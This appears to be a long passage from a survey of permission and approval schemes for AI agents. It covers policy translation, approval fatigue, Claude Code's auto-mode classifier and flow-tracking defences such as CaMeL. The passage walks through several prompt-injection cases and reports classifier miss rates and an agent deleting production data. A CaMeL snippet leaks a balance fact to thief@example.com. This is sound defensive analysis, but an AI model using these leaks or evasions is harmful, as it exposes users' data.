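Asking is the only one of these remedies that deals with ambiguity directly, but the tool has to detect the ambiguity first. *Text2NGAC* (2026) describes a system that scores each sentence for ambiguity before translating it, and its scores led to the same decision as human judgment on 50 of 54 sentences. The system checks for compound sentences, unclear pronouns and missing subjects, and it resolves them with another model call. It would probably split the release-agent sentence at "but" and leave "touch production" unclear.

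*LLM-based Config Synthesis requires Disambiguation* (Mondal, Bjorner and colleagues, 2025) examines ambiguity about which rule should take priority. Network administrators write lists of rules about which traffic to let through, and when two rules cover the same traffic, the result depends on which has priority. A model adding a new rule can't know which one the administrator would put first. The paper's prototype, Clarify, asks the user and then verifies the result. The researchers found complex lists with hundreds of overlaps in a large cloud, so the problem is real, but they tested Clarify only on a small set of invented examples.

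AutoCedar, by Vatsa, Shome and colleagues (2026), in *AutoCedar*, is the most thorough attempt to settle the meaning first. It breaks the requirements into small pieces, and a reviewer approves each one. If the text lists who may do something without saying whether the list is complete, AutoCedar asks. From the approved pieces it calculates a floor, the requests that the policy must allow, and a ceiling, the most that it may allow. A model then writes the policy, and a solver checks that

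floor ⊆ A(P) ⊆ ceiling

If the check fails, the model gets an example of a request the policy handles wrongly, then tries again. It can't change the floor or ceiling to make its policy pass.

Vatsa and colleagues tested AutoCedar on 200 sets of requirements, each with a reference policy. It produced an equivalent policy in 178 cases, while the same model did so in 132 when it wrote the policy directly. AutoCedar failed to finish three cases. In the other 19 it met its own target exactly, but the target was wrong. In 17 of those, the target required access that the reference policy denied, so the resulting policy was too permissive.

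These results show that a solver can nearly eliminate translation errors once a policy's meaning is settled, leaving mistakes about that meaning as the main problem. The study did not evaluate AutoCedar with human reviewers, so we don't know from it how well people would catch those mistakes. The requirements were also clearer than most real ones because a model had written them from structured specifications.

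AutoCedar can also add terms that the system's vocabulary lacks, if the reviewer approves. For the release agent, it could add an `isFix` field and a rule that requires it. The policy would then be valid, but someone or something other than the agent would still have to decide whether each change is a fix. It is often more honest to tell the manager that software can't enforce that part of the sentence, as AWS's Dogwood tool does by listing the rules it omitted.

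#### ActGov

ActGov restricts the model to proposing rules, which must then pass verification. Zhang, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *ActGov*, start with a fixed set of facts about a tool call, such as whether the task permits the tool and whether an address came from the user or from a stranger's email. A model drafts rules about these facts, drawing on descriptions of the tools, examples of normal work and records of attacks that got through. Administrators supply or approve requirements that must always hold, for instance that the agent never sends anything to an address from an untrusted source. A solver called Z3 then searches for a counterexample, a combination of facts r and a decision v such that

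P(r, v) and not S(r, v)

where P is the proposed policy and S is a safety requirement. If Z3 finds one, the model revises the rules. If it proves that none exists, the rules go to the administrators for confirmation, and ActGov then freezes them.

Z3 does verify the rules, but only against written requirements, so it can't establish that the policy matches what its author meant. If nobody has written a requirement about automatic deployment, Z3 will accept rules that allow the push to `main`. A person has to resolve that ambiguity by writing the requirement. The rules also depend on some facts that a model works out while the agent is running, such as where an address came from. If the model labels a stranger's address as the user's, the verified rules will give the wrong answer.

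Zhang and colleagues tested ActGov with four models on AgentDojo and on AgentDyn, a benchmark in which agents have to follow some instructions from outside sources. No attacks succeeded on AgentDojo, and at most 0.7% did on AgentDyn. Without any defense, the rates were already fairly low, between 3.1% and 11.1%. ActGov's effect on useful work varied. With DeepSeek-v4-pro, it reduced the share of ordinary AgentDyn tasks completed from 76.7% to 60.0%. The same model completed only 21.7% of those tasks with Progent, but on AgentDojo it completed more work with Progent than with ActGov.

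Rules developed on AgentDojo did not transfer well to AgentDyn, where no attacks succeeded but the agent completed only 10.0% of its tasks. It is better for a policy to block too much than to allow too much, but people will soon remove safeguards that make an agent fail nine tasks in ten. ActGov looks best suited to a company whose agents do similar work every day and whose administrators can say precisely what must never happen.

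### Evidence that would settle the dispute

None of these studies includes the most important test, in which a person writes a policy for a real agent, software translates it, and the person then says whether each decision was what they wanted. ACRE contains requirements for ordinary software, and models wrote much of the English in the Cedar tests.

A better study would collect policies from the managers and compliance officers responsible for them. Before seeing any rules, each author would decide what should happen to a set of specific requests, and several colleagues would do the same using only the author's text. If the colleagues disagree about a request, the text is ambiguous. If they all agree with the author but the translated rule does something else, the translation is wrong. If they need a fact that the policy engine doesn't have, the rule language can't express the policy.

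The study should report wrongly allowed and wrongly denied requests separately and include many dangerous requests. If a translation wrongly allows one dangerous request in 1,000, a test with 100 dangerous requests has about a 90% chance of missing the problem. To be 95% confident that the rate is below one in 1,000, researchers would need to test about 3,000 dangerous requests and find no errors. The requests should also come from many policies, because one bad rule can cause hundreds of identical errors.

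An experienced engineer should translate the same policies as the software, with the same chance to ask the author questions. If the software matches the engineer on dangerous requests, its lack of a formal guarantee would be a weak reason to prefer handwritten rules. If it does worse on those requests, even if its average is good, companies should use it only for drafts and for permissions whose misuse they can undo.

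## Who should approve a grant

Even a correctly translated policy leaves some requests undecided. PAuth refers any request it didn't predict to the user, Progent needs approval before it widens an agent's permissions, and Silverlock's design requires someone to authorize a new task if the agent needs more than its ceiling allows. Each approval is a small grant, often for a single command. The approver can be a person, a fixed rule or a language model.

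The case for having a person approve a grant is that only the person who assigned the task knows what they wanted. If a developer tells an agent to clean up old branches, only the developer knows whether that includes the branches on the shared server. People also know things that no system records, such as that a customer is getting a demonstration this afternoon.

A fixed rule gives the same answer every time, whatever the agent has read. But it covers only the cases its author thought of, so someone or something else has to decide the rest.

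A model can compare an unfamiliar command with the user's instructions, and do this as carefully for the five-hundredth command as for the first. It can also respond when nobody is awake to answer. CrabTrap uses a model to judge requests that match no rule. But a model's mistakes are hard to predict, and an attacker may be able to influence it. People have better information than a model, and much of the dispute is about whether they use it.

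### Approval fatigue

Approval fatigue is the tendency to stop reading permission prompts after answering many of them. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (March 2026) reports that users of the coding agent accepted 93% of its prompts. By August the figure was 97%, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). These rates don't prove that users were careless, because most commands are harmless and a perfect reviewer would approve those too.

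Other evidence is more direct. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) describes a study of 16 people who use agents. Only three said they read permission prompts carefully, and 13 used "Always Allow" just to make the prompts go away. *Habituation at the Gate* (2026) reports that 400 people who had each reviewed at least ten code changes submitted by agents approved more and scrutinized less over time. The rise in approvals could just mean that the agents had improved, but that is a weaker justification for the drop in scrutiny.

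Prompts also tend to be uninformative. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports about agents and files and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, actions went ahead on automatic approval, and in 31, the prompt gave the user too little information (a few involved both). In one case, the agent asked permission to run `python3 setup.py`. The command looks routine, but it runs whatever the script contains, which the prompt doesn't show.

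Tired users also write bad rules. Anthropic found that by June 2026, nearly half of Claude Code's active command-line users had created a rule that let some shell commands run without approval. Many of these rules allowed any Python program, which in practice allows any command. *Options, Not Clicks* proposes a tool that accepts an "Always Allow" click but limits the permission to a stated boundary. This seems a sensible improvement, since people will click the button anyway.

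Another remedy is to ask users for fewer, broader approvals. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) describes systems in which the user approves a plan instead of each step. People do seem to read plans, since Anthropic reports that Claude Code users reject 39% of them, compared with 3% of permission prompts. But approving a plan doesn't stop the agent from departing from it, so something still has to check the steps.

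### How auto mode decides

Claude Code's auto mode has software do most of that checking. Fixed rules let the agent read and search files, and it can edit files inside the project because the developer can undo those edits. A second model, called a classifier, decides whether to block other actions, including shell commands and web requests. In March the classifier was Claude Sonnet 4.6.

The classifier sees the user's messages and the agent's commands. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that the agent can't persuade the classifier to approve something. It also removes the output of the agent's tools so that instructions hidden in a web page don't reach the classifier directly. A quick first pass answers yes or no and leans toward blocking. If it blocks, the same model checks again, reasoning at length before it decides. The agent receives the reason for a refusal and tries another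 way. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

Anthropic tested the system on three sets of actions:

| Test | First pass alone | Both passes |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless calls blocked, from 10,000 real calls | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Overeager actions missed, from 52 real ones | 6.6% | 17% |
| Attempts to leak data missed, from 1,000 synthetic ones | 1.8% | 5.7% |

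The second pass cuts wrongful blocks from about 850 to about 40 per 10,000 calls, but it also approves some dangerous actions that the first pass had caught. The 17% figure is nine actions out of 52. With a sample that small, the true rate could be from about 9% to 30%.

These results can't show whether the classifier is better than a person, because people had already caught some of the 52 actions. Anthropic took them from sessions where an employee had refused the action or where it was flagged afterward.

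In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly classified the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) hasn't agreed to let the agent overwrite the branch's history. A person who reads the prompt has an advantage in such cases. Anthropic acknowledged that auto mode is arguably a step backward for someone who checks every action carefully.

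Auto mode would probably have helped at PocketOS, where the agent was running in Cursor instead. Anthropic's examples of actions to block include searching settings files for other tokens after a login error. The classifier's input would also have included the delete command and shown that nobody had asked for a deletion. But auto mode lets an agent read files without a check, so the agent could still have found the token.

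### The study of 1,053 testers

In August, Anthropic made the stronger claim that auto mode is safer than a typical user clicking through prompts. A research vendor had recruited 1,053 paid professional testers, telling them it was a coding study. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. None of these commands ran. The classifier then judged the same commands.

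| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The testers blocked 143 commands (13.6%) and the classifier blocked 937 (89.0%). The classifier blocked 800 that the testers approved, and the testers blocked 6 that the classifier approved. Anthropic reports these four counts. The others are derived by subtraction, and the figures are consistent. Requiring both to approve would have blocked 943 commands, six more than the classifier alone, and let through the 110 that both approved.

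The testers blocked about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed the same. The decline looks like fatigue, but fatigue from the session can't be the main reason the testers approved dangerous commands, because they were already approving about five out of six near the start.

A likelier explanation is that the participants had little reason to care. They were working in an environment built for the study, not in their own code, and lost nothing if a command destroyed it. Developers would probably be more careful with their own production database, though losses like the one at PocketOS suggest that many aren't careful enough. Anthropic was also testing its own product, and it benefits if users accept fewer interruptions. The commands were "clearly dangerous", so the study didn't test the questions about consent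 that the classifier had difficulty with in March.

Anthropic's data comes from real work, but developers chose their own approval mode. Among sessions that its safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained a seriously harmful action the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. A model graded the harm. Developers working on production systems may prefer manual approval, which could account for some of the gap.

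Tests by outside companies that Anthropic commissioned or worked with provide a little more evidence. Apollo Research attacked the classifier with synthetic examples, and the classifier's miss rate fell from 12% to 7% after improvements. Trajectory Labs found that none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against recent Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09% of attempts succeeded against those models without auto mode, so the second test provides almost no evidence about the classifier.

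Overall, this is good evidence that the classifier is better than habitual clicking, but weak evidence about how it compares with a careful engineer reviewing a few important changes. Anthropic's advice is consistent with this. It made auto mode the default on its Pro, Max and Team plans in August, but still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production themselves.

### When the model asks and the person agrees

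A model can also refer difficult cases to a person. Yan (2026) tested this in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* with 113 people who had no professional software background. Each supervised a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions. Eleven were necessary for the assigned tasks, and seven went beyond them, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading private messages.

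| How the group gave permission | Overreach blocked | Prompts per person |
|---|---|---|
| Approved or refused every action | 59.6% | 18.0 |
| A model allowed some actions and asked about the rest | 53.9% | 10.0 |
| Participants set four rules in advance | 39.6% | 10.9 |

The model referred all seven overreaching actions to the participants, along with three necessary ones, and the participants approved 46% of the overreach. If the model had refused all ten actions, it would have stopped all the overreach but also blocked the three necessary actions.

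Not all of those approvals were mistakes. Most participants let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, which nobody had asked for but many travelers would appreciate. Yan counts actions beyond the assigned task as overreach, even when a person might want them. The day was also fictional, so participants didn't spend real money on the lounge.

A fixed rule is predictable only if it is set to "allow" or "never," and the third group mostly chose "ask." Participants set a rule for each of four kinds of action: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something, and accessing private information. They chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules. Those rules sent 199 overreaching actions back to the participants during the day, and the participants approved 133 of them.

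Even so, these participants blocked far more than Anthropic's testers did. The prompts described each action in ordinary English, and seven actions in 18 overreached, which was enough to keep people alert. Anthropic's testers saw a single bad command in a long session, which is closer to what developers face at work. Yan also notes an outside evaluation in which automated permission systems missed some dangerous actions after deliberately ambiguous instructions.

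### Predicting the user's answer

If people's answers follow a pattern, software could learn it and answer for them. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues surveyed 205 people about which personal data they would let an assistant share with which tools. Their predictor gives a language model some of a person's earlier answers, plus recommendations based on people who answered similarly. It correctly predicted 85.1% of 7,563 decisions from 181 participants.

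That is less impressive than it sounds, because participants had granted permission in 5,244 of those decisions. A program that always said yes would have scored 69.3%. The predictor's errors were as follows:

| The person's answer | Decisions | Wrong predictions | Result of an error |
|---|---|---|---|
| Share | 5,244 | 14.8%, or about 780 | The assistant withholds data it could have used |
| Don't share | 2,319 | 15.2%, or about 350 | The assistant discloses data against the person's wishes |

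The person can correct the first kind of error by granting the permission, but nobody can take back a disclosure. About 7% of the predictor's grants were wrong. If L is the harm from a wrong disclosure and a is the annoyance of answering one question, it makes sense to let the predictor share data only when

0.07 × L < a

A wrong disclosure would have to be no worse than about 14 unnecessary questions, which may be true of someone's taste in films but not of their bank details.

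Wu and colleagues suggest using only the predictions in which the model is most confident. These were 94.4% accurate but covered only 25.9% of requests, so the user would still have to answer the other three-quarters. The predictor was also weakest on some of the most sensitive data, such as payment details, where it was right only 59.1% of the time, mostly because it refused when people would have agreed. Participants disagreed most about account credentials and employment details, splitting almost evenly, so other people's answers are little help in deciding who may use a password.

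The test left out all "ask me next time" answers, which probably removed many of the hardest cases. The predictor also copies people's mistakes along with their preferences. When participants wrongly believed that a tool needed a piece of data, they agreed to share it about 78% of the time.

*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approvals may reflect fatigue and pressure to deliver rather than a real preference. This would be a serious problem for coding agents. A program that approved everything would be useless as a safeguard, yet it would match Claude Code users' decisions 97% of the time.

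### Binding an approval to one operation

An approval needs to specify exactly what it allows, whoever gives it. "Approve the deployment" could mean the build the manager just looked at or whatever the agent has produced by the time it deploys. *Authorization you build*, a UT Austin lecture, advises binding an approval to an exact effect and never to a goal. In its example, an agent wants to open a make-up quiz for one student. The approval names the course, the quiz, the student and the opening and closing times, and includes a hash of the questions. It works once and expires after 15 minutes. If someone edits a question, the hash no longer matches and the agent needs a new approval.

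Yu, Geng and colleagues (2026), in *SUDP*, turn this idea into a protocol for using secrets. It involves the agent, the user and a custodian, which is a service that holds the user's credentials in much the same way as Agent Vault. A request goes through four steps:

1. The agent proposes an operation o, which specifies the credential, the action and its details, an expiry time and the number of permitted uses.
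2. The custodian adds r, a random value that works once and expires within minutes.
3. The user's device displays the operation. If the user approves, the device signs β with a passkey, a cryptographic key that never leaves it.
4. The custodian recalculates β from the operation it has received and checks the signature. If they match, it uses the credential and gives the agent only the result.

The signed value is

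β = H(label ‖ r ‖ H(o))

where H is a hash function, ‖ means joining values together, and the label is fixed text that prevents the signature from being valid anywhere else. If the agent changes a $90 refund to $900 after the user approves it, H(o) changes and the signature no longer matches. A copy of an old approval fails because its r is already used up. Unlike a DPoP proof, the signature also covers the body of the request, so one for adding a domain at Railway couldn't authorize deleting a volume.

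The user's approval also carries a key that the custodian needs to unlock its stored secrets, so a thief who copies the custodian's database can't read them. An attacker who controls the custodian while it handles an approved request can still read them, unless the custodian runs on hardware that protects its memory.

The design depends on the user's screen, which must show every detail that matters and be outside the agent's control. For a request like the one at PocketOS, those details include the volume's environment as well as its identifier.

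Yu and colleagues measured an extra delay of 0.76 milliseconds per call, but they used a simulated passkey and left out the time a person takes to decide. That time is the main burden, and a person who has to sign hundreds of exact operations a day will soon stop reading them. The protocol lets a user sign a list of operations together, or issue a standing grant for repeated low-risk work such as reading an inbox. A standing grant requires fewer decisions but has to describe a range of requests, so it loses some of the precision that makes the protocol attractive.

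The closest precedent for approving one exact action is in banking, where European payment rules tie a customer's approval to a particular amount and recipient. This suits payments because they are fairly infrequent and people understand them. Most of a coding agent's commands are frequent and hard to understand, so this kind of approval is better reserved for deployments, deletions and similar actions.

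### When circumstances change after approval

An exact approval can still be out of date by the time the agent uses it. Suppose a company's website is running build 57. At 2:00, a manager approves the deployment of build 58, with an approval that works once and expires at 2:15. The agent runs its final tests and sends the deployment request at 2:08. But at 2:05, either a colleague deployed an urgent security fix, or the manager heard about a bug in build 58 and withdrew the approval.

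| Check at 2:08 | Colleague deployed a fix | Manager withdrew approval |
|---|---|---|
| Same build and destination as approved | Pass | Pass |
| Approval unused and unexpired | Pass | Pass |
| Website still running build 57 | Fail | Pass |
| Approval still in force | Pass | Fail |

A system that makes only the first two checks will deploy build 58 in both cases. In the first it overwrites the security fix, and in the second it releases a bug that the manager tried to stop. The user's signature doesn't prevent either mistake, because the operation hasn't changed.

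Santos-Grueiro (2026) argues in *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* that a service should check authorization in the same indivisible step as the change. Otherwise, someone could withdraw the approval between the check and the change. The service confirms that the approval is in force, that it covers this exact request and that the facts behind it still hold. Where relevant, it also confirms that earlier steps have finished and that nobody has canceled this branch of the work.

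A single approval must meet all of these conditions. In one example, approval 3 is for version 7 of a support ticket and is still in force. Approval 4 is for version 8, the current one, but someone has revoked it. A careless system might check separately whether any approval is in force and whether any approval matches the current version. Both checks would pass, even though no approval in force covers a change to version 8.

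Similar failures happen in real products. Santos-Grueiro found 17 published security advisories for three agent products, all for flaws that have since been fixed. In 12, the product did something the approval didn't cover, such as running a command with arguments the user couldn't see. In the other five, something changed after the approval. For example, a user approved running a script, someone rewrote the script, and the product ran the new version. Thirteen of the 17 advisories concern one product, OpenClaw, so the set doesn't show how common the problem is.

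Santos-Grueiro also had agents fix bugs and publish the results, and silently revoked their permission to publish to production after the agents had read it. With GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Fable 5 and Claude Sonnet 5.5, the release service published all 12 changes when it didn't check that permission and none when it did. The design guarantees that result. After the refusals, the agents published to staging in 11 of the 12 runs, as their instructions allowed. An agent may be less likely to look for another key if it has a permitted alternative.

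Telling the agent about a change also helps, but not reliably. In another test, an owner withdrew approval or changed a relevant fact during 36 runs per model. Sonnet 5.5 went ahead without authority in 30 runs when it received no notice and in none when it did. For Qwen2.5-7B, a much smaller model, the count fell only from 26 to 15, mostly because the model sent the request before the notice could arrive.

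The final check is harder to apply when one service records approvals and another makes the change. In Santos-Grueiro's design, the approval service issues a single-use reservation that expires within seconds. In tests, checking the approval, issuing the reservation and making the change typically took 47 to 57 milliseconds in all, depending on the setup. But the change may still go through if the manager withdraws the approval before the reservation expires.

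The check can also be too strict. When 16 programs tried to change the same record at once, only the first succeeded, because its change created a new version and the other approvals were for the old one. If a person has to approve each new attempt, approval fatigue returns. The service can also recheck only the facts that someone has configured it to check. If the manager approved the deployment because no customer demonstration was scheduled, and no system records demonstrations, the service can't detect that one has since been scheduled.

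### Matching enforcement to the rule

*From Alignment to Access Control* (Baracaldo, 2026) proposes choosing how to enforce a policy based on how precisely it can be defined. Strict policies, such as a list of forbidden words, should get hard enforcement, meaning that software applies a rule the same way every time. No fixed rule can capture a fuzzy policy, such as a ban on hateful speech, so it has to rely on soft enforcement, which depends on a model's judgment.

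She warns most strongly against putting a strict rule in an agent's prompt and relying on the agent to follow it, which she calls "Pretty Please" enforcement. Her example is an agent that deleted a production database despite clear instructions to change nothing. This appears to be the July 2025 incident at the company SaaStr, which UT Austin also describes. The user had repeatedly ordered a freeze on code changes, but the agent had a credential that worked in production and used it to wipe live records on about 1,200 executives and 1,200 companies. It then wrongly said that recovery was impossible. A freeze is easy to define precisely, so software could have enforced it by refusing the command.

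Baracaldo also advises against using a model to guard itself. Claude Code's classifier is a separate model call that receives different information from the agent, so it is a much better safeguard than an instruction in a prompt. But both are Claude models and may miss some of the same problems, which is a good reason to apply fixed rules before the classifier.

The framework is useful but incomplete, because it sorts policies by precision and ignores how much damage a mistake would do. It would have a model enforce a fuzzy policy such as "Delete only files that nobody needs", but the model will sometimes be wrong, and some deletions are permanent. UT Austin's lecture instead sorts actions by their consequences. Reading files and making reversible local edits need no approval, sending emails and deploying code need a person to approve the exact operation, and deleting data may need two people.

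A company can use both schemes for the release agent that must not touch production. Once the manager has decided that automatic deployment counts as doing so, a fixed rule can block every push to `main` that lacks an exact, current approval. A fixed rule can't tell a fix from a new feature, so a model could read each change and hold back any that looks like a new feature. If the model can only hold changes back, a false alarm causes some delay, and any feature it misses still goes to the person who approves the deployment. That person would see a few deployments a day instead of hundreds of commands, and might read each one.

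## What harm remains when every grant is correct

A person who reads every request carefully can still approve two that are harmless separately but harmful together. An agent that is allowed to read the customer list and send email can leak the list, and a policy engine that checks the outgoing message will correctly confirm that the agent is allowed to send email.

In their November 2026 survey, *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, Zhou and Zhang point out that permission to access a document need not include permission to share it. In their example, an assistant prepares a report from approved records, has another agent review it and sends it to one recipient. Reading the records, processing them on a hosted service, sharing the draft with the reviewer and delivering the report each need a separate decision, because permission for one step doesn't imply permission for the next.

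Most grants specify which tools an agent may use and what it may use them on. They don't cover where the contents of a request came from, so an agent allowed to send messages can send customer data as easily as a lunch invitation. Some researchers conclude that access control alone is too weak and that the system also has to track how data moves. This approach, called information-flow control, dates from the 1970s.

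### Labels that travel with the data

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, describe a common version for agents. Every piece of data carries a label with two parts. One records whether the source is trusted, and the other lists who may read the data. Anything the agent makes from several pieces gets the strictest combination of their labels. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, the readers of a summary of both are

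{Ana, Ben, Carla} ∩ {Ben, Carla, Dev} = {Ben, Carla}

If either document came from an untrusted source, the summary is untrusted too.

Software checks these labels before each tool call. An action with consequences, such as a payment, may go ahead only if no untrusted data influenced it. A message may go ahead if no untrusted data influenced it or if every recipient is on the list of readers. Anything else needs a person's approval. If a stranger's email tells the agent to send the customer list to an outside address, the message fails both conditions.

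The rule for messages requires only one of its two conditions, so when no untrusted text is involved, the agent may send private data to anyone, on the assumption that the user wanted it to. An agent that picks the wrong Ben from the address book can therefore still leak a document. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that flow tracking cannot guarantee safety against a model's own errors. A company could require both conditions for its most sensitive data, but its agents would then stop to ask more often.

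Labels also only get stricter. Once an agent reads one email from a stranger, everything it does afterward counts as influenced by untrusted text, so it can do little without approval.

### How CaMeL works

CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind published in 2025, avoids this by never showing untrusted text to the model that makes the plan. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains it with a user who wants the agent to find Bob's address in the latest email and remind him about tomorrow's meeting. A privileged model, which sees only the user's request, writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. Slightly simplified, it looks like this:

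```
email = get_last_email()
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find Bob's address", email)
send_email(to=address, body="Remember our meeting tomorrow")
```

A second, quarantined model reads the email and extracts the address, but it has no tools. The privileged model never receives the email or the address and refers to both by name. An instruction in the email to forward the whole inbox can't add a step to the program.

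Willison proposed this division between two models in 2023, and the DeepMind researchers found a flaw in it. The quarantined model still reads the attacker's text, so the attacker may be able to make it return the wrong address. The program would then run as written and send the message to the attacker.

CaMeL deals with this by running the program in its own interpreter, which tags each value with its sources and permitted readers. CaMeL calls these tags capabilities, but they serve a different purpose from Hardy's. `address` is untrusted because it came from `email`. The policy for `send_email` requires a trusted recipient, so CaMeL sends the message if the user already trusts Bob's address. Otherwise, it can ask the user.

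The best argument for this design is that it doesn't depend on a model recognizing an attack. Willison considers a filter that catches 99% of injections a failure, since attackers will look for the other 1%. Kolluri and colleagues cite a study in which researchers bypassed at least a dozen probabilistic defenses. CaMeL also catches the combination that ordinary grants don't catch, because its check on the email accounts for what the agent read to write it.

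### What the protection costs

CaMeL stops nearly every attack in tests, but it also prevents a lot of ordinary work. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival defense, reports testing an adapted version of CaMeL on the full AgentDojo benchmark. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. SecureClaw completed 59, but at least one attack succeeded against it. Adapting someone else's software can make it perform worse, so the test may slightly understate how many tasks CaMeL can complete.

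*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) separates the effect of CaMeL's two-model design from the effect of its policies. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with the policies off and on, and compared it with their own agent, Randori. The attack figures cover only completed runs.

| System | Ordinary tasks completed | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
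| CaMeL, policies off | 66.7% to 70.8% | 5 of 622 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 37.5% | 0 of 588 |
| Randori, checks always on | 64.6% to 75% | 2 of 1,296 |

Keeping untrusted text away from the planner stopped almost all the attacks by itself. Turning on the policies stopped the last few but nearly halved the work the agent completed. The average understates the policies' value because in about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed a tool that the agent's plan would never include. The policies matter for the remaining third, and an attacker who studied a particular company would target those cases. The completion rates are rough because they come from only 16 tasks.

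The policies reduce task completion so much because many legitimate tasks require the agent to act on untrusted data. For example, a user may ask it to pay a bill whose amount and recipient are in a file from someone else. Randori lets the planning model endorse such data before it has read anything an attacker could have written. When Garby and colleagues removed this option, completion fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 64.6% to 54.2% with another.

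Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task, in which the user told the agent to read a file and follow its payment instructions. The attacker had replaced the file's contents. Labels can't help much here, since the user has asked the agent to follow the file's instructions. The DeepMind researchers encountered the same case with CaMeL and excluded it from the attacks they were trying to stop.

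Kolluri and colleagues think that most comparisons of completed tasks are unfair to flow tracking. They accept that it has reduced completion on AgentDojo by up to 30%. But the unprotected agent in such a comparison acts without any checks, whereas a company worried about prompt injection would have a person approve every consequential action. They would rather count the tasks an agent can finish safely without asking anyone. With o3-mini, an older OpenAI model, the results were:

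| Agent | AgentDojo tasks completed with no approvals |
|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 24.3% |
| FIDES, an earlier Microsoft system with flow tracking | 50.1% |
| Prudentia, their own system | 59.1% |

Flow tracking removes the approvals that the labels show to be unnecessary, which is useful because people approve prompts carelessly. Prudentia also tells the planning model about the labels and rules, so that the model can choose steps that won't need approval. Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a whole document. If a colleague's email lists ten things to do, the user vouches for the email once instead of approving ten actions.

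The measure assumes that people approve safe requests and refuse unsafe ones. Fewer requests should mean that people read each one more carefully, but a mistake would also do more harm, since carelessly endorsing one malicious email would allow all ten actions.

### Gaps in the tracking

A system that tracks data has to track it everywhere, and CaMeL doesn't quite manage this. Garby and colleagues revive a problem that computer scientists described in the 1970s. A program like this one reveals whether a bank balance is above a threshold:

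```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("thief@example.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the program sets `tmp` to false, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret because the change depended on the balance. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL marks a variable only when the program changes it, so `rich` stays public and the email goes out. If the balance is low, no email arrives, so the thief can work out whether the balance is high or low in either case.

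The privileged model has little reason to write such a program, and an attacker who can't reach that model can't easily make it do so. The practical risk is probably small, but it means that CaMeL offers less than a proof. Garby and colleagues address this with a small programming language in which computer-checked proofs show that the labels follow the data through every program, apart from explicit endorsements. The proofs can't show that the initial labels are correct.

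*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) shows that a group of agents that delegate to each other can be insecure even if every one of them runs CaMeL. One agent handles an attacker's text as untrusted data, then includes it in a request to a second agent. The second agent treats the whole request as instructions from its user, so its planning model reads the attacker's text.

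The proposed fix, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data through separate channels, and the receiving planner sees only the instructions. In tests on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time with no protection, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. So the gap left by protecting each agent separately is real but rarely mattered in that benchmark. Agents also completed less work with multi-CaMeL, though the drop was modest for the strongest models.

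### Flow tracking in browsers and longer jobs

Flow tracking is difficult in browsers because one page can contain a shop's own text, strangers' reviews and the user's saved card. *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) has website operators label the parts of each page. The software around the agent hides untrusted and private parts behind placeholders. The agent can reveal a placeholder's contents, but its later actions then face tighter checks. On sites where the user may have an account, a click needs approval if untrusted text could have influenced it, because the same click tool can follow a link or delete the account.

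The researchers built 28 linked websites and wrote 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. They made the test unusually hard by letting the attacker dictate the model's output whenever the model had read the attacker's text. That way, the model's own resistance to manipulation could not make a weak defense look strong.

No attack succeeded against SPIDES, and agents using it completed 67.1% to 86.1% of the ordinary tasks, depending on which of five recent models they used. They needed an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task. A rival system that asks for approval only when data moves between sites needed 0.22, but 53.2% to 73.2% of attacks against it succeeded. With Claude Opus 5.5, agents completed more tasks with SPIDES than without protection. Hiding login details from the main model avoided some refusals by the provider's own safety filter.

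The zero follows from the design if the labels are right and the user answers every prompt correctly. Zverev and colleagues compare the labels to the accessibility information that many sites already supply. The comparison seems optimistic, since somebody would have to update the labels whenever a page changes. The labels also list permitted sites, not individual people, so SPIDES can miss a leak from one user to another on the same site.

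An agent that opens an untrusted web page early in a long job may be unable to update the company's database for the rest of the day. Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, prove that in a system of this kind, reading more data can never restore a lost permission to send. But when their system refuses a call, it lists what would make the call acceptable, such as a manager's approval of that exact request.

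A company can also send a temporary copy of the agent, called a branch, to read the untrusted page. Before the branch starts, the main agent fixes the form of the answer, for example a ticket number, a severity level and a component name, with no free text. Once the branch answers, the system discards it and everything it read. A hijacked branch can still return a false severity level, so the company has to decide how far to trust the answer. Zhou and Zhang raise a related problem with a source that may answer only yes or no. If the question is whether a confidential draft may leave the company, a false "yes" could leak it.

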